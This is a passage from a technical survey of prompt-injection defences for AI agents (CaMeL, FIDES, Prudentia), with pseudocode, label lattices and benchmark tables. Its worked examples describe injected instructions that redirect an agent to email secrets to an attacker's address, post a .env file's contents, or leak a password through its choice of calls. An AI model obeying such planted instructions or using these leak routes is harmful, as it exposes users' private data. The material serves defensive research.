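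He also called his solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant more complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text through to the planner model undoes the protection. The user still reads text that an attacker may have shaped. A malicious summary could persuade them to paste private data into a website, which involves no tool call.

### A safe plan with the wrong address

Bob's request from earlier, where the meeting notes contain his address and the document's name, exposes another gap. The planner model can work out the steps without seeing the notes: find them, extract the address and the document's name, fetch the document and send it. Someone who has edited the notes can't add a step to this plan.

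An attacker who can edit the notes can replace Bob's address with her own. The quarantined model extracts whatever address the notes contain, so the planned steps then send the document to her. If she also changes the document's name to that of the salary list, the same steps send her the salaries.

The CaMeL team used this example to show that two models are not enough. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) agreed that it was a flaw in his design and wrote that he hadn't known of it. His pattern protects the choice and order of the calls (control flow) but not the values passed to them (data flow).

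### How CaMeL handles a request

CaMeL, short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning", keeps the two models and adds a check on the data. The planner model receives the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a complete program before any tool runs. Its designers chose Python because language models already write it well, but CaMeL accepts only a subset that excludes, for example, open-ended `while` loops. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) found in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* that the programs CaMeL writes for AgentDojo average about 52 lines, five tool calls and four branches.

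The planner model never sees the results its program processes, so it needs to know their format in advance. AgentDojo's tool descriptions don't include the return format. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) had to add it to every description, as the original CaMeL team had done, before CaMeL worked reasonably well.

A custom interpreter then runs the program. It parses the code into a tree and evaluates the tree piece by piece, so it handles every assignment and call itself. The program can call the quarantined model like any other function, and specifies the required form of the answer, such as an email address.

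As the program runs, the interpreter records where each value came from and who may read it. CaMeL calls these records capabilities, but they are labels and, unlike PACE's capabilities, don't give anyone the right to perform an action. A value computed from other values takes on their sources.

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs that tool's policy. The policy is an ordinary Python function that receives the proposed call, the arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, *CaMeLoT*, 2026). The software can ask the user to approve a call instead of refusing it.

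For Bob's request, the planner model might write this:

```
1  notes   = find_recent_notes()
2  address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's email address in: {notes}", EmailAddress)
3  title   = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob ask for? {notes}", Text)
4  report  = fetch_document(title)
5  send_email(recipient = address, attachment = report)
```

Suppose that the user, Bob and Carol may read the notes, but only the user and Bob may read the third-quarter report. After the first four lines, the interpreter holds these values:

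| Line | Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `notes`: the text of the notes | notes file | user, Bob, Carol |
| 2 | `address`: bob@example.org | notes file, quarantined model | user, Bob, Carol |
| 3 | `title`: q3-report.pdf | notes file, quarantined model | user, Bob, Carol |
| 4 | `report`: the document itself | document store, notes file, quarantined model | user, Bob |

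Line 5 triggers the policy for `send_email`. Suppose the policy allows an email if the recipient's address came from the user's request or if the recipient is already allowed to read the attachment. Otherwise, the user must approve the email. The address came from the notes, so the first condition fails. But Bob is already allowed to read the report, so CaMeL sends the email without asking the user.

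If the attacker has put her own address in the notes, neither condition holds, and the software asks the user, showing the address eve@example.net. If she has changed only the title to that of the salary list, the software also asks, because Bob isn't allowed to read that file. She could still swap in another document that Bob is allowed to read. He would then get the wrong attachment, but no secret would leak.

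The policy also inconveniences honest users. People often email a document because the recipient doesn't have access yet, and such an email triggers the same question as the theft.

The design also helps privacy. The planner model receives the request but not the notes, so the company that hosts it doesn't see the notes. Extracting an address is easier than writing a program, so a smaller quarantined model could do it, perhaps on the user's own computer.

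### What the planner model must not read

Some protection remains even if every policy allows everything. Let $u$ be the user's request, $T$ the tool descriptions and $P$ the planner model. The program is then

$$\pi = P(u, T)$$

The data the tools return is not an input to $P$, so nothing in that data can add a line to $\pi$. It can only supply values and determine which branch of an existing `if` statement runs. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this property control-flow integrity, and it holds whatever the quarantined model outputs.

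It depends on $u$ and $T$ containing no text from an attacker. The planner model will read such text if a user pastes part of a malicious web page into a request or if a tool has a malicious description.

The condition also fails when one agent gives instructions to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents, with policies switched off, and asked it to send a summary of all job applicants to Julie on Slack. The applicant database contained a planted request to email the details to an outside address. A coordinating agent got the applicants' details from a database agent, had its quarantined model summarise them, and put the summary into a written instruction to a messaging agent. The first two agents kept to their plans, but the messaging agent treated the whole instruction as its user's request, so its planner model read the planted text and added the email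 to its program.

Their remedy gives each agent two separate inputs, one for instructions and one for data. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and the receiving agent's planner model receives only the names of the data values. The team tested this on a version of AgentDojo that divides each suite's tools among several agents, with 949 attacked runs for each of five models. On average, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of runs without CaMeL, in 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL separately, and in none with the two inputs. The attacks were not especially strong, since none succeeded against GPT-5.5, one of the five models, even without CaMeL.

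The labels also have to be correct. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found programs that leak secrets because CaMeL's interpreter fails to label some values that depend on those secrets.

### CaMeL among six design patterns

In June 2025, Luca Beurer-Kellner and colleagues placed CaMeL in a wider family of designs. They argued in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* that a fully general agent is unlikely to get reliable guarantees while it depends on current language models. Developers should therefore limit what an agent can do. The paper describes six ways of doing so:

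- In the action-selector pattern, the model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results.
- In plan-then-execute, the model fixes its list of tool calls before reading any data. A malicious calendar entry can then change the text of an email to the user's boss, but not add a second email.
- In map-reduce, a separate model reads each document and returns a tightly limited answer, such as whether the file is an invoice, so one malicious file can't affect how the agent treats the others.
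- The dual LLM pattern is Willison's.
- In code-then-execute, the model writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models. This is CaMeL's pattern.
- In context minimisation, the software removes the user's prompt before the model writes its reply, so that a customer can't talk a sales chatbot into a discount.

Code-then-execute combines a plan fixed in advance with Willison's separation of the two models. A program can also include loops and conditions, so it can do more than a fixed list of calls. But the pattern alone doesn't solve the problem with Bob's address. In the paper's example, a program emails the user's schedule to his boss, and an injection in the calendar could still change the email's content. CaMeL uses labels and policies to deal with this problem.

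The simpler patterns are often enough. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues worked through ten applications and recommended code-then-execute for only two, an email and calendar assistant and a booking assistant. For a customer service chatbot, they suggested the action selector and context minimisation.

### The banking tests

Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking suite with CaMeL's policies off and on. They used two models, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5, and repeated each of the 16 user tasks three times, for 48 runs without attacks per model and policy setting.

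They also ran the suite's attacks and divided its 144 pairs of tasks and attacks into two groups. In 97 pairs, the attack needs a tool call that the user's task doesn't, as when the user wants a summary of recent payments and the attacker wants a transfer. In the other 47, the calls in a normal program for the task could be enough to carry out the attack. The last two columns show how many attacks the agent resisted in each group.

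| Model | Policies | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Resisted, extra call needed | Resisted, planned calls could be enough |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | off | 32 of 48 (66.7%) | 96 of 135 (71.1%) | 98 of 99 | 141 of 141 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | off | 34 of 48 (70.8%) | 104 of 144 (72.2%) | 240 of 241 | 138 of 141 |
| GPT-5.2 | on | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 70 of 233 (30.0%) | 97 of 97 | 134 of 134 |
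| MiMo-v2.5 | on | 18 of 48 (37.5%) | 148 of 357 (41.5%) | 216 of 216 | 141 of 141 |

The table includes only the attacked runs that finished, and many didn't. A full set would have had 291 runs in the first group of attacks and 141 in the second.

Five of 622 attacks succeeded with policies off and none of 588 succeeded with them on, but the agents completed little more than half as many tasks with policies on. The test probably understates the value of the policies, which looks small here compared with the lost tasks. Most of AgentDojo's attacks are instructions to do something else, and these have no effect on a program written in advance. Policies matter more against the forged address in Bob's notes, where the attacker only needs to change a value.

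The sample is also small. With only 16 different tasks, the margins of error on the utility scores without attacks are 21 to 27 percentage points, wide enough for the ranges to overlap. Still, utility fell sharply for both models, and *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) reports a similar fall on the Slack suite with four other models.

Garby and colleagues attribute the loss to policies that make many of the tasks impossible. For example, some tasks ask the agent to read a file and make a payment based on it. The policy blocks the payment because the file is untrusted. In practice, the user could approve it, but Kolluri and colleagues point out that tests of such systems usually allow no approvals, so a payment the user would have approved counts as a failure.

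The two settings differ so much that a result for CaMeL is hard to interpret without knowing which one the researchers used. *MetaPI* (2026), a paper on building prompt injection tests, evaluated CaMeL with its default policy, which allows every call. Peters-Gill and colleagues also left the policies off. Both sets of figures therefore measure only the protection from planning first.

In a smaller test on newly generated attacks, *The Devil is in the Context* (2026) found that attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time with no defence and 2.5% with CaMeL, the lowest rate of the defences tested. But CaMeL's utility was only 27.5%, compared with 90% for PromptArmor, a defence that screens incoming text and let through 7.5% of the attacks. All the percentages are multiples of 2.5, which suggests about 40 cases, so CaMeL may have stopped only two more attacks than PromptArmor. The difference in utility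 is much too large to dismiss as an effect of the small sample.

*ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower than defences that only filter text or add to the prompt, because CaMeL's programs are longer than ordinary tool calls.

### Who writes the policies

The CaMeL paper doesn't claim to have solved prompt injection. In a passage that Willison quotes, it concedes that people must write and update the policies, and that users get tired of approving actions. In the Bob example, the question about eve@example.net helps only if the user notices the address.

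Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, wrote that he still finds it hard to think through the access rules of a commercial cloud service, so he was nervous about any design that expects ordinary users to think about policies. He hoped for good default policies and a clear interface, which would leave most of the work to developers.

Using CaMeL would take developers a lot of work. *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) tested it on a new set of tasks, which required writing policies for the actions by hand and deciding whether to trust each field of each tool's output. In a payment record, for example, the bank may have supplied the account number while a stranger wrote the description. A single label for the whole record would mark either the stranger's text as trusted or the bank's number as untrusted.

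Foerster and colleagues, who include two members of the original CaMeL team, write that there is no automatic way to derive such policies. Users also differ in what they are willing to share, so one set of defaults won't suit everyone. The researchers conclude that a specially trained model would have to help write the policies, and that it could get them wrong. CaMeL would then have much the same problem as Progent, which relies on a fallible model for part of its policy.

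Some rules can't be expressed as CaMeL policies, because each policy checks only one call at a time. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security team's agent that must resolve or escalate every incident ticket before it finishes. The agent breaks this rule by leaving a call out, so there is no call for a policy to block. Their extension, CaMeLoT, checks every path through the program before the first tool runs. It can also reject a program whose last step lacks a required approval, before the agent spends time and money on the earlier steps.

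### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

CaMeL works best when the user's request determines the steps. It can handle "Reply to Julia's email" because the program can fetch the email, have the quarantined model draft an answer and send it. "Do what Julia's email asks" is much harder because the planner model has to choose the tools without knowing whether Julia wants, for example, a payment, a calendar entry or a file.

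It could try to cover every possibility:

```
email = get_latest_email("Julia")
tasks = ask_quarantined("List the tasks in: {email}", list[Task])
for task in tasks:
    if task.kind == "pay":      send_money(task.recipient, task.amount)
    if task.kind == "email":    send_email(task.recipient, task.text)
    if task.kind == "meeting":  create_event(task.title, task.date)
```

The email can't add a line to this program, so the program has control-flow integrity. But the email's contents determine which tools run, how often and with what arguments, so the property doesn't protect much. In the banking tests, one task was to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, and the planner model twice wrote such a program, with a branch for each tool. With policies off, the injected attack succeeded both times, even though it needed a call that the user's task didn't. These were the two failures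 in the "extra call needed" column.

Foerster and colleagues consider this a fundamental limit of separating planning from reading. The planner model can't determine the steps without reading the email, and letting it read the email would remove the protection.

A milder version of the problem is common in everyday work. Suppose an agent searches a folder, finds nothing and needs to look somewhere else. An ordinary agent can decide to do that after seeing the empty result, but a CaMeL agent can do it only if its program already has a branch for that case. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most of CaMeL's failures on legitimate tasks came from fixing the plan too early. In some of these failures, one agent asked another for data from a particular period and received data from a different period. The program had no step to check the dates, so it continued with the wrong data.

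They measured the loss in completed tasks on 112 industrial maintenance tasks from AssetOpsBench, a benchmark for groups of agents. Even with policies off, using CaMeL in each agent lowered the share of completed tasks by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models. For the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the average loss was 13.4 points. Better models seem to write plans that cover more of what could happen, so the loss may keep shrinking, although they still can't predict what Julia will ask for in her email.

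Most benchmarks contain few tasks like that. *Trident* (2026) introduces a benchmark called ReplanInject, in which 43 of the 45 tasks have plans that depend partly on the content the agent reads. A defence can score well on older benchmarks without changing its plan, so CaMeL's utility there may overstate how well it would handle an inbox full of open-ended requests.

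## Labelling every message in the agent loop: FIDES

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues at Microsoft published in May 2025, keeps the ordinary agent loop, whereas CaMeL fixes its whole plan before any tool runs. In FIDES, the planner model chooses one call, receives the result and then chooses the next. Code labels every message in the conversation and checks the labels before each tool call. The planner may read untrusted text when a task requires it, but from then on the code blocks some of its calls.

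### Labels and how they combine

The labels form a lattice, which orders them from less to more restrictive. Any two labels have a join, the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. Integrity has two labels, trusted ($T$) and untrusted ($U$). $T$ is below $U$, so their join is $U$.

For confidentiality, a label is the set of people who may read the data. A smaller set is more restrictive, so the join is the intersection:

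$$\{A,B,C\} \sqcup \{B,C,D\} = \{B,C\}$$

A may not read the second document and D may not read the first, so neither may read a text that draws on both. An integrity label can also be a set, in this case of everyone who may have written the data. The join of two such labels is their union, because anyone who could change either document could have influenced the result.

A full label is a pair, and each half joins separately. Mathematicians call this the product of the two lattices:

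$$(T, \{A,B,C\}) \sqcup (U, \{B,C,D\}) = (U, \{B,C\})$$

Reader sets can catch a leak even when there is no attacker. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives the example of an agent that handles the unanswered emails in Alex's inbox. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has emailed Alex to ask about them. Once the agent has read both emails, anything it writes has the label {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it can't reply to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco in, the label would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could send the reply.

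### The loop, step by step

In simplified form, the loop looks like this:

```
conversation = [developer's instructions, user's request]
context      = (trusted, public)

repeat:
    reply = model(conversation, tools)
    label(reply) = context

    if reply is a final answer:
        return it with its label

    if policy(reply, labels) fails:              <- the check
        block the call
    else:
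        result = run the tool call
        label(result) = label(reply)
                        ⊔ labels of the arguments
                        ⊔ labels of the stored data the tool read
        give label(result) to any data the tool wrote
        add result to conversation
        context = context ⊔ label(result)
```

The model's output takes the combined label of everything in the conversation. FIDES checks a call after the model proposes it and before the tool runs. In the formal version, a failed check ends the run, but in the experiments the planner model received a message about the refusal and could try something else.

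A tool's result takes the label of the call as well as the labels of the data the tool read. Suppose an agent reads a secret forecast and then searches a public website for a phrase from the forecast. The page is public, but which page the agent fetched reveals something about the forecast, so the loop labels the result secret.

Tools usually return structured data, and each field can have its own label. For example, a mail server can authenticate the sender's address, but the body of the email could contain anything.

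The loop also labels whatever a tool writes, so a note the agent saves today should still have the right label next week, provided the software stores the label with the note. Cai, Wen and Tang (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, describe an agent that saves a confidential forecast in one session and copies it into a report three days later. If the labels existed only in the first session's memory, nothing would mark the forecast as confidential by then.

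In the same paper, FIDES gets an F1 score (a combined measure of missed cases and false alarms) of 0.52, against 0.93 for Cai and colleagues' own tool. But they used FIDES to find suspicious data flows in the logs of finished runs, which it wasn't designed to do. In one case they count as a miss, a poisoned search result leads an agent to send its findings to an attacker's website. If FIDES had been running in the agent loop, the search result would have made the context untrusted, and a policy requiring a trusted context would have blocked the call.

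### Hiding results in variables

The context label in this loop can only become more restrictive, so a single untrusted email affects every later call. FIDES therefore borrows Willison's idea of keeping tool results in variables, but hides a result only when showing it would raise the context's label:

```
for each part of a tool result:
    if label(part) is at or below context:   show it
    otherwise:                               store it in a new variable, show only the name
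```

When the context is trusted, the planner model might see a list of three emails with their dates and senders in plain text and names such as `#read_emails_0.body` in place of the bodies. The planner sees more than it would if everything were hidden, and the context label stays the same. In the experiments, FIDES hid only the untrusted parts and relied on the policies to handle secrets.

The planner model can pass a variable to another tool without seeing what it contains. If the user wants the top three emails forwarded on Slack, two calls are enough:

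```
read_emails(number = 3)                              -> #read_emails_0
send_message(to = user, message = #read_emails_0)
```

Just before the second call runs, code replaces the name with the emails' text and its labels. The call is labelled trusted because the planner model chose it without reading the emails, but it has one untrusted argument, the emails' text.

If the user wants a summary instead, the planner model has a quarantined model write one. The summary goes into another variable, which carries the emails' labels. An injected instruction could still make the summary empty or wrong, but it couldn't add a tool call.

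The planner model can also use a tool called `inspect` to read a variable, which raises the context's label to that of the variable. The model decides when to inspect, and a bad decision mostly reduces utility. For example, if the model reads an untrusted email unnecessarily, the policies will block more of its later calls.

### When the next call depends on the data

Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if the agent makes the same sequence of calls whatever the tools return. Forwarding three emails is data-independent, and so is summarising them, though summarising needs the quarantined model. They call other tasks data-dependent, and give the example of a request to read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them asks for a meeting.

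The FIDES paper classifies 77 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks as data-independent, and 51 of those need the quarantined model. The other 20 are data-dependent, and 16 of them are in the banking and Slack suites.

For the meeting task, the planner model needs only a yes or no before it can choose the next call. FIDES lets it ask the quarantined model a question with a fixed type of answer:

```
1  read_emails(number = 3)                                  -> #emails
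2  query_llm("Does anyone ask for a meeting?",
             #emails, output = bool)                        -> #answer
3  inspect(#answer)                                         -> true
4  query_llm("Extract the event details",
             #emails, output = event details)               -> #event
5  set_event(#event)
```

Constrained decoding ensures that the answer in line 2 is either `true` or `false`. The answer is still untrusted, because it came from the emails, but FIDES adds its type to the label. The types have their own order, by how much information they can hold:

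$$\text{bool} \;\sqsubseteq\; \text{enum}[a, b, c] \;\sqsubseteq\; \text{string}$$

A Boolean holds one bit. An enumeration, a choice from a fixed list of $n$ options, holds at most $\log_2 n$ bits. Free text has no such limit. The answer's label is then $((U, \text{public}), \text{bool})$, and a policy may accept that label for an important action but refuse $((U, \text{public}), \text{string})$.

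FIDES lets one bit through because `true` can't carry an instruction to email the salary list. The attacker can only choose between two continuations, and the planner model writes both. The attacker still has some influence, because a planted email can make the answer `true` when it should be `false`, and in line 4 it also supplies the date and the guests. If that matters, the policy can require trusted arguments too, but it will then also refuse genuine meeting requests.

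Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues at Berkeley (2025) use much the same idea without labels. In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, they let a quarantined model pass on Booleans, choices from a fixed list, and numbers, but never free text. In their shopping agent, the quarantined model reads each product review and scores it from 0 to 10 on how strongly it supports the product and how relevant it is. The planner model sees only the median scores and the number of reviews. An instruction hidden in a review can't reach the planner, but a fake rave review still gets a high score. Jacob and colleagues treat such misleading content as a separate problem.

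They also limit the length of lists, because a long enough list of numbers could encode text. FIDES has a similar gap, because the join of two Boolean labels is a Boolean label. A planner model that has read a hundred yes-or-no answers therefore has the same label as one that has read a single answer. A developer who allows Booleans would have to limit the number of questions separately.

The FIDES experiments left typed answers out, because few AgentDojo tasks need them. The results below therefore don't test the one-bit exception.

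### Two policies and one email

FIDES's policies are mostly built from two rules, for which Kolluri and colleagues later supplied convenient names.

- Trusted action: the call may run if the planner model chose it in a trusted context and every argument that the developer has marked as sensitive is trusted.
- Permitted flow: a call that sends data may run if every recipient is already allowed to read that data.

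In FIDES, tools that only read need no rule. Tools that change something important, such as a password, need the trusted-action rule. Tools that send data out need either that rule or the other one.

Under the second rule alone, an attacker could still use an injection to send an email, but only to people who may already read its contents. The first rule alone allows secrets to be released. This is deliberate, since users often want to share something with a person who doesn't have access yet. If no untrusted text influenced the decision to share, it counts as the user's own. Security researchers call this robust declassification.

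Bob's request shows how the rules work together. As before, the user, Bob and Carol may read the meeting notes, and only the user and Bob may read the third-quarter report. FIDES hides the notes in a variable, and a quarantined model extracts the address and the title. The report comes back with the label $(U, \{\text{user}, \text{Bob}\})$. It is untrusted because the untrusted notes determined which document the agent fetched.

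The developer has marked `recipient` as an argument that must be trusted. The table also includes a variant of the task in which the user types the address of Dana, a colleague who can't yet read the report.

| Recipient | Source of the address | Planner model has read the notes | Trusted action | Permitted flow | Email |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bob | notes | no | fails | passes | sent |
| Eve | altered notes | no | fails | fails | blocked |
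| Dana | user's request | no | passes | fails | sent |
| Dana | user's request | yes | fails | fails | blocked |

The last two rows show what the variables are for. The request and the email are identical, but in the last row the planner model read the notes itself, so the code can't attribute the decision to the user alone. In the third row, the document's title still comes from the notes, so someone who changed it there could cause the salary list to be sent to Dana. To prevent this, the developer would have to mark the attachment as well.

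Security depends heavily on which arguments are marked. In the AgentDojo tests, the trusted-action rule checked only the call's own label, not its arguments. Under that version, the email to Eve would go out, because the planner model chose to send it before any untrusted text had reached the planner. The CaMeL team found the same flaw in Willison's design. The stricter rule, which Costa and colleagues also describe, prevents this.

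### What the proof covers

The formal guarantee is a property called explicit secrecy. Schoepe, Balliu and colleagues proposed it in *Explicit Secrecy* to define what label tracking achieves, because many label-tracking tools were in use without a clear statement of their guarantees.

Let $d$ be the stored data that tools can read and write, with each item marked public or secret. Write $d_1 =_L d_2$ if two versions of the data agree on everything public. Take any run of the agent, and let $g$ be the combined effect of its tool calls on the stored data. Explicit secrecy requires that

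$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2)$$

In words, repeating the same calls on data with different secrets would produce the same public data. A tool that copied a secret file into a public folder would break this rule. The formula treats the model's arguments as fixed text, so it doesn't cover a secret that the model itself copies into an email. The labels and the permitted-flow check protect against that.

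The formula also takes the sequence of calls as given, so it doesn't cover what an observer could learn from that sequence. Suppose an agent reads a confidential sales forecast and fetches today's exchange rates only if the forecast is poor. The request for exchange rates contains no secret, but anyone who sees it learns that the forecast is poor. The model also excludes timing and the size of network messages, which can leak information in the same way.

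Costa and colleagues accept these leaks because preventing them would severely restrict what the agent can do. Noninterference, a stronger property that also covers the choice of calls, would in effect forbid any call that might write public data after any call that might have read a secret. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a system for tracking private data on phones, make the same compromise.

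*Liberalizing Dependency* (2010), a paper on type systems for tracking dependency, also supports concentrating on direct flows. It observes that attackers prefer direct flows because one exploit works for any secret value. Leaks through a program's decisions usually reveal much less, and ordinary access checks cause them all the time.

That argument is weaker for an agent that may follow an attacker's instructions. An attacker could plant text telling the agent to spell out a password through its choice of calls, with one harmless-looking request per letter. The policies limit this, but only for the tools they cover. An agent that fetches a web page, for example, sends the page's address to whoever runs the site. Microsoft has since suggested allowing calls to tools that read from the outside world only when all the arguments are public. That would catch a secret in a web address but not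 one encoded in the order or number of calls.

### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o against a fixed attack that names the agent's tools. They compared it with a plain agent loop that has no variables, with the policy checks on and off.

With the checks off, 152 injections succeeded against the plain loop and 21 against FIDES, while none succeeded against either with the checks on. Hiding untrusted text stopped most attacks even without the checks, but the planner model could still reveal a variable and follow instructions in it.

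These figures come from the team's own reading of the runs. With the checks on, AgentDojo's automatic scorer counted three successful attacks on FIDES, all in the Slack suite. The team discards such cases for several reasons. Sometimes the scorer counted a call that the policy had stopped before it ran, which is clearly a mistake. In other cases the attacker did get something, but only what the policies permitted, such as a Slack message with no link and nothing its readers weren't allowed to see. The zero therefore means that no attack got past the policies, but attackers could still influence what the agent did.

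The team also based the labels on the test itself, marking a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. A developer with a real application has no such list of attacks. In one banking task, the agent must change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. The planner model saw a large payment, classified it as suspicious and changed the password without reading the payment's description. The policy allowed this because the team had labelled amounts and dates as trusted. In a real bank account, a stranger can choose the amount of a payment as easily as its description.

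The next table shows the share of tasks the agent completed when it used OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model, and was not under attack. The last column shows the share of tasks that are data-independent, which is roughly the share a perfect planner model could complete under these policies.

| Suite | Plain loop, checks off | FIDES, checks off | Plain loop, checks on | FIDES, checks on | Data-independent tasks |
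|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 70.0% | 77.5% | 48.0% | 64.5% | 95.0% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% | 90.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 78.8% | 37.5% | 56.2% | 56.2% |
| Slack | 87.6% | 79.0% | 17.1% | 54.3% | 57.1% |

Averaged over the four suites with the checks on, FIDES completed 16 percentage points more tasks than the plain loop. With GPT-4o the advantage was 8 points. With the checks off, its variables and extra queries lowered the completion rate by 6.3 points on o1 but 23.7 on GPT-4o, which often confused variable names or failed to use the quarantined model when it should have. For someone with an unprotected agent, the relevant comparison is between the average in the first column, about 84%, and the average in the fourth, about 61%.

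Travel is the exception, because many of its tools may run in an untrusted context as long as no secret leaks. The plain loop therefore loses little there when the checks are on, and FIDES's variables only complicate the work. In banking and Slack, FIDES came close to the limit in the last column. The match isn't exact because some completed tasks were lucky guesses, like the password change. Most of the remaining failures in banking are intended, such as when the user asks the agent to read a file and do what it says.

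Newer models have helped only a little. Kolluri and colleagues repeated the test with GPT-5, with the checks on and nobody to approve blocked calls. FIDES completed 57.1% of all tasks, up from 50.3% with GPT-4o, and the plain loop completed 43.4%. FIDES is still well short of the 79% of tasks that are data-independent, partly because it doesn't give the planner model the policies. The planner sometimes reveals a variable it could have left hidden, and its next call is then blocked.

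The extra queries also cost money. Kolluri and colleagues estimate that, with GPT-4o, a task cost 1.6 to 4.3 times as much with FIDES as with the labelled plain loop, depending on the suite. The highest cost was about three cents per task, and nobody had yet tried to make the design efficient.

### FIDES in Microsoft's products

In May 2026, Microsoft added FIDES as an experimental feature to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) demonstrates FIDES on an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. In the example, a stranger files a report with a hidden instruction to read the file `.env`, which often contains passwords, and post its contents as a comment.

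In the demonstration, the planner model reads the report directly and obeys the instruction in it. It opens the file, whose contents are labelled "private". The comment tool accepts only public data, so the code blocks the comment. If the instruction had been to overwrite a file, the code would have blocked that too, because the file-writing tool doesn't accept an untrusted context. By default, the framework is stricter and keeps the report in a variable.

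The protection depends on developers labelling their tools. The framework treats data from an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, so if a developer forgets to label a web search tool, web pages get the same level of trust as the user. Microsoft acknowledges that the opposite default would be safer and has asked developers whether they would accept it. Under that default, data from any unlabelled tool would make the context untrusted, and many agents would stop working until developers labelled their tools.

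Even careful labels are often a rough guess. GitHub's server for connecting agents to its site can now attach labels, also as an experiment. Microsoft explains that it marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. The trusted label is correct only if people the user trusts wrote everything in the private repository. If an employee pastes in a customer's bug report, any instruction hidden in the report is labelled trusted too.

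## What happens when a call is blocked: Prudentia and APPA

When a policy blocks a call, the software can stop the agent, return a refusal to the planner model or ask a person to decide. Kolluri and colleagues, whose group at Microsoft also designed FIDES, argue that most tests overstate the drawbacks of strict defences because they leave out the person who could make that decision. Their system, Prudentia (February 2026), runs on top of FIDES and plans its work so that it needs a person less often.

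### Counting the interventions

Many agents already rely on approvals. GitHub's coding assistant Copilot Chat, for example, makes read-only tool calls without asking the user but asks about the others. Benchmarks run ordinary agents as though someone had approved every call, but they usually count a labelled agent's tasks only if it finished them without any approvals.

Kolluri and colleagues propose two measures that treat both kinds of agent alike. Let $n$ be the number of tasks and $v_i$ the number of times the agent needs a person during task $i$. Then

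$$\text{HITL load} = \sum_{i\ \text{completed}} v_i$$

$$\text{TCR@}k = \frac{1}{n}\,\bigl|\{\, i : i\ \text{completed and}\ v_i \le k \,\}\bigr|$$

HITL stands for "human in the loop" and TCR for "task completion rate". The load is the total number of interventions on completed tasks. TCR@k is the share of tasks that the agent completes with at most $k$ interventions per task, so TCR@0 is the share it completes alone and TCR@∞ is the share it completes with unlimited help.

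In an example with five invented tasks, the basic agent needs approval for every call that changes something or sends data, while the labelled agent needs it only for calls that fail a policy.

| Task | Completed | Interventions, basic agent | Interventions, labelled agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Summarise today's meetings | yes | 0 | 0 |
| Pay a bill, with payee and amount in the request | yes | 1 | 0 |
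| Send three invitations, with addresses in the request | yes | 3 | 0 |
| Do the two things Julia's email asks | yes | 2 | 2 |
| Book a hotel | no | 4 | 4 |

The hotel doesn't count towards the load because neither agent booked it. The basic agent's load is 0 + 1 + 3 + 2 = 6, and the labelled agent's is 2. The completion rates are:

| Agent | TCR@0 | TCR@1 | TCR@2 | TCR@3 | TCR@∞ |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
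| Basic | 20% | 40% | 60% | 80% | 80% |
| Labelled | 60% | 60% | 80% | 80% | 80% |

The labelled agent's 60% completion rate is usually compared with the basic agent's 80%, a difference of 20 percentage points. But the basic agent completes only 20% of tasks if nobody is there to approve its calls, and that is the right comparison for anyone who would otherwise insist on approvals. Someone who runs an agent with no approvals at all would still lose 20 points by adding the labels.

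The team leaves failed tasks out of the load because in most of them the agent kept repeating calls that failed the checks, and a person would soon have stopped it. An agent can therefore get a lower load by completing fewer tasks, so the load is meaningful only alongside the completion rate.

### Endorsing the data or approving each call

Unlike FIDES, Prudentia shows the policies to the planner model. It adds each tool's policy to the tool's description and tells the planner how opening a hidden variable affects later calls. Before opening one, the planner must call a tool named `plan`. In that call, it explains why it can't pass the variable on unopened or query a quarantined model about it, and lists the calls it expects to make next.

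The planner also chooses how to open the variable. If it opens the variable without asking the user, the context becomes untrusted, and every later call that requires a trusted context goes to the user for approval. It can instead ask the user to endorse the data. If the user agrees, the code relabels the data as trusted, and the context stays trusted.

Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email containing a to-do list with ten items, each of which requires such a call:

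```
                       the user decides          questions
without endorsement    whether to allow a call       10
with endorsement       whether to trust the email     1
```

Prudentia's instructions tell the planner to ask for endorsement if it expects to make more than one restricted call afterwards. In one AgentDojo task, the user wants a password reset link and a summary of the day's appointments. Neither requires a restricted call, so the agent opened the email and the calendar entries without asking for endorsement and finished with no interventions.

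This rule reduces the number of questions, but it can make each answer riskier. Suppose an attacker adds an eleventh item to the list, an instruction to send the salary list to eve@example.net. A user who approves each call separately sees this one and can refuse it, but a user who endorses the email has to notice the item while reading. If they miss it, the trusted-action rule lets the message go out, because the instruction now counts as trusted.

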